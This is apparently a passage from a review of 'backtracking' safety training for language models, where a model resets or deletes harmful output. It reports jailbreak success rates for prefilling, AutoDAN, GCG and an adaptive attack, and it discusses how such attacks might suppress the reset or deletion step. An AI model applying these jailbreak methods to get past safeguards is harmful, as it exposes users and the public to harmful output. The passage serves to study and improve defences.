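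Gemma reset in 60.6% of its responses to harmful requests and Llama in 49.9%, much more often than these figures would require, so many resets probably discarded text that was still harmless. In the safety tests, Llama's first useful token arrived about a second later on average, and output speed fell by about 12%. The models almost never reset in tests unrelated to safety.

Zhang and colleagues also tested four attacks, assuming the attacker has a copy of the model's weights but can't block the reset token in the deployed system. The table shows how often each attack succeeded with ordinary training and with trained backtracking.

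| Attack | Gemma-2-2B | Llama-3-8B |
|---|---|---|
| Prefilling: the response starts with a phrase of agreement | 50.4% → 11.6% | 85.0% → 2.6% |
| AutoDAN: a program varies handwritten jailbreak prompts | 82.0% → 60.0% | 84.0% → 37.0% |
| GCG: a program searches for text to add to the request | 77.0% → 32.0% | 62.5% → 16.5% |
| Adaptive: the GCG search also tries to prevent a reset | 82.0% → 27.5% | 73.0% → 21.0% |

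The defence helped against every attack, but AutoDAN still succeeded more often than the adaptive attack, which was designed specifically to defeat the defence. The adaptive attack was therefore probably not the strongest possible, and a version based on AutoDAN might do better. Zhang and colleagues conclude that none of the models is adequately protected.

A full reset is wasteful when one sentence in a long answer is harmful. *Backtracking for Safety* (2025) proposed returning to any earlier point and replacing only the harmful passage. *Reinforcement Learning with Backtracking Feedback* (Sel, Keshava and colleagues, 2026) simplified this by having models output the kind of violation and the number of tokens to delete, then continue. To create training examples, the researchers inserted harmful passages into good answers, so the correct continuation was already available.

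The models were then trained on their own outputs, which a second model, the critic, scored. A response that was safe throughout earned 1 point, and so did a successful correction. The penalty was 0.5 points for an unnecessary deletion, 0.2 for a failed correction and 1 for an uncorrected violation. A model therefore earns no more for avoiding harmful text than for writing it and then deleting it. Unless the system buffers its output, the user may see the harmful text before it is deleted.

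Attacks using harmful requests from a collection of chatbot conversations succeeded 1% to 2% of the time against models that could delete their output and retry, compared with 24% to 28% against the original Gemma 2 and Llama 3 models. In one test, blocking the deletion command raised the rate from 1% to 18%. An attack designed to suppress the command succeeded 4.7% and 4.3% of the time on two sets of requests, the same as the ordinary version of the attack. Since blocking the command raised the rate so much, this attack probably failed to suppress it, but a better one might.

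Training with a critic that was right 82% of the time, instead of about 98%, still gave rates of 2% to 4%. Scores on tests of knowledge, reasoning and mathematics hardly changed, but those tests don't measure how often a model deletes harmless text about sensitive subjects.

Trained backtracking avoids part of the retry problem because the new attempt isn't independent of the old one. In Zhang and colleagues' tests, responses after a reset were almost always safe, so *b* was close to zero on the second attempt. However, the same model writes and judges the text, and an attack that affects its writing may also affect its judgement, so a separate guard is still useful. After the guard rejects a response, the system can ask the model for a refusal or a safe alternative instead of another answer to the same request. Zhang and colleagues mention a simpler option, a fixed refusal, which doesn't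 give the model another chance to write something harmful.
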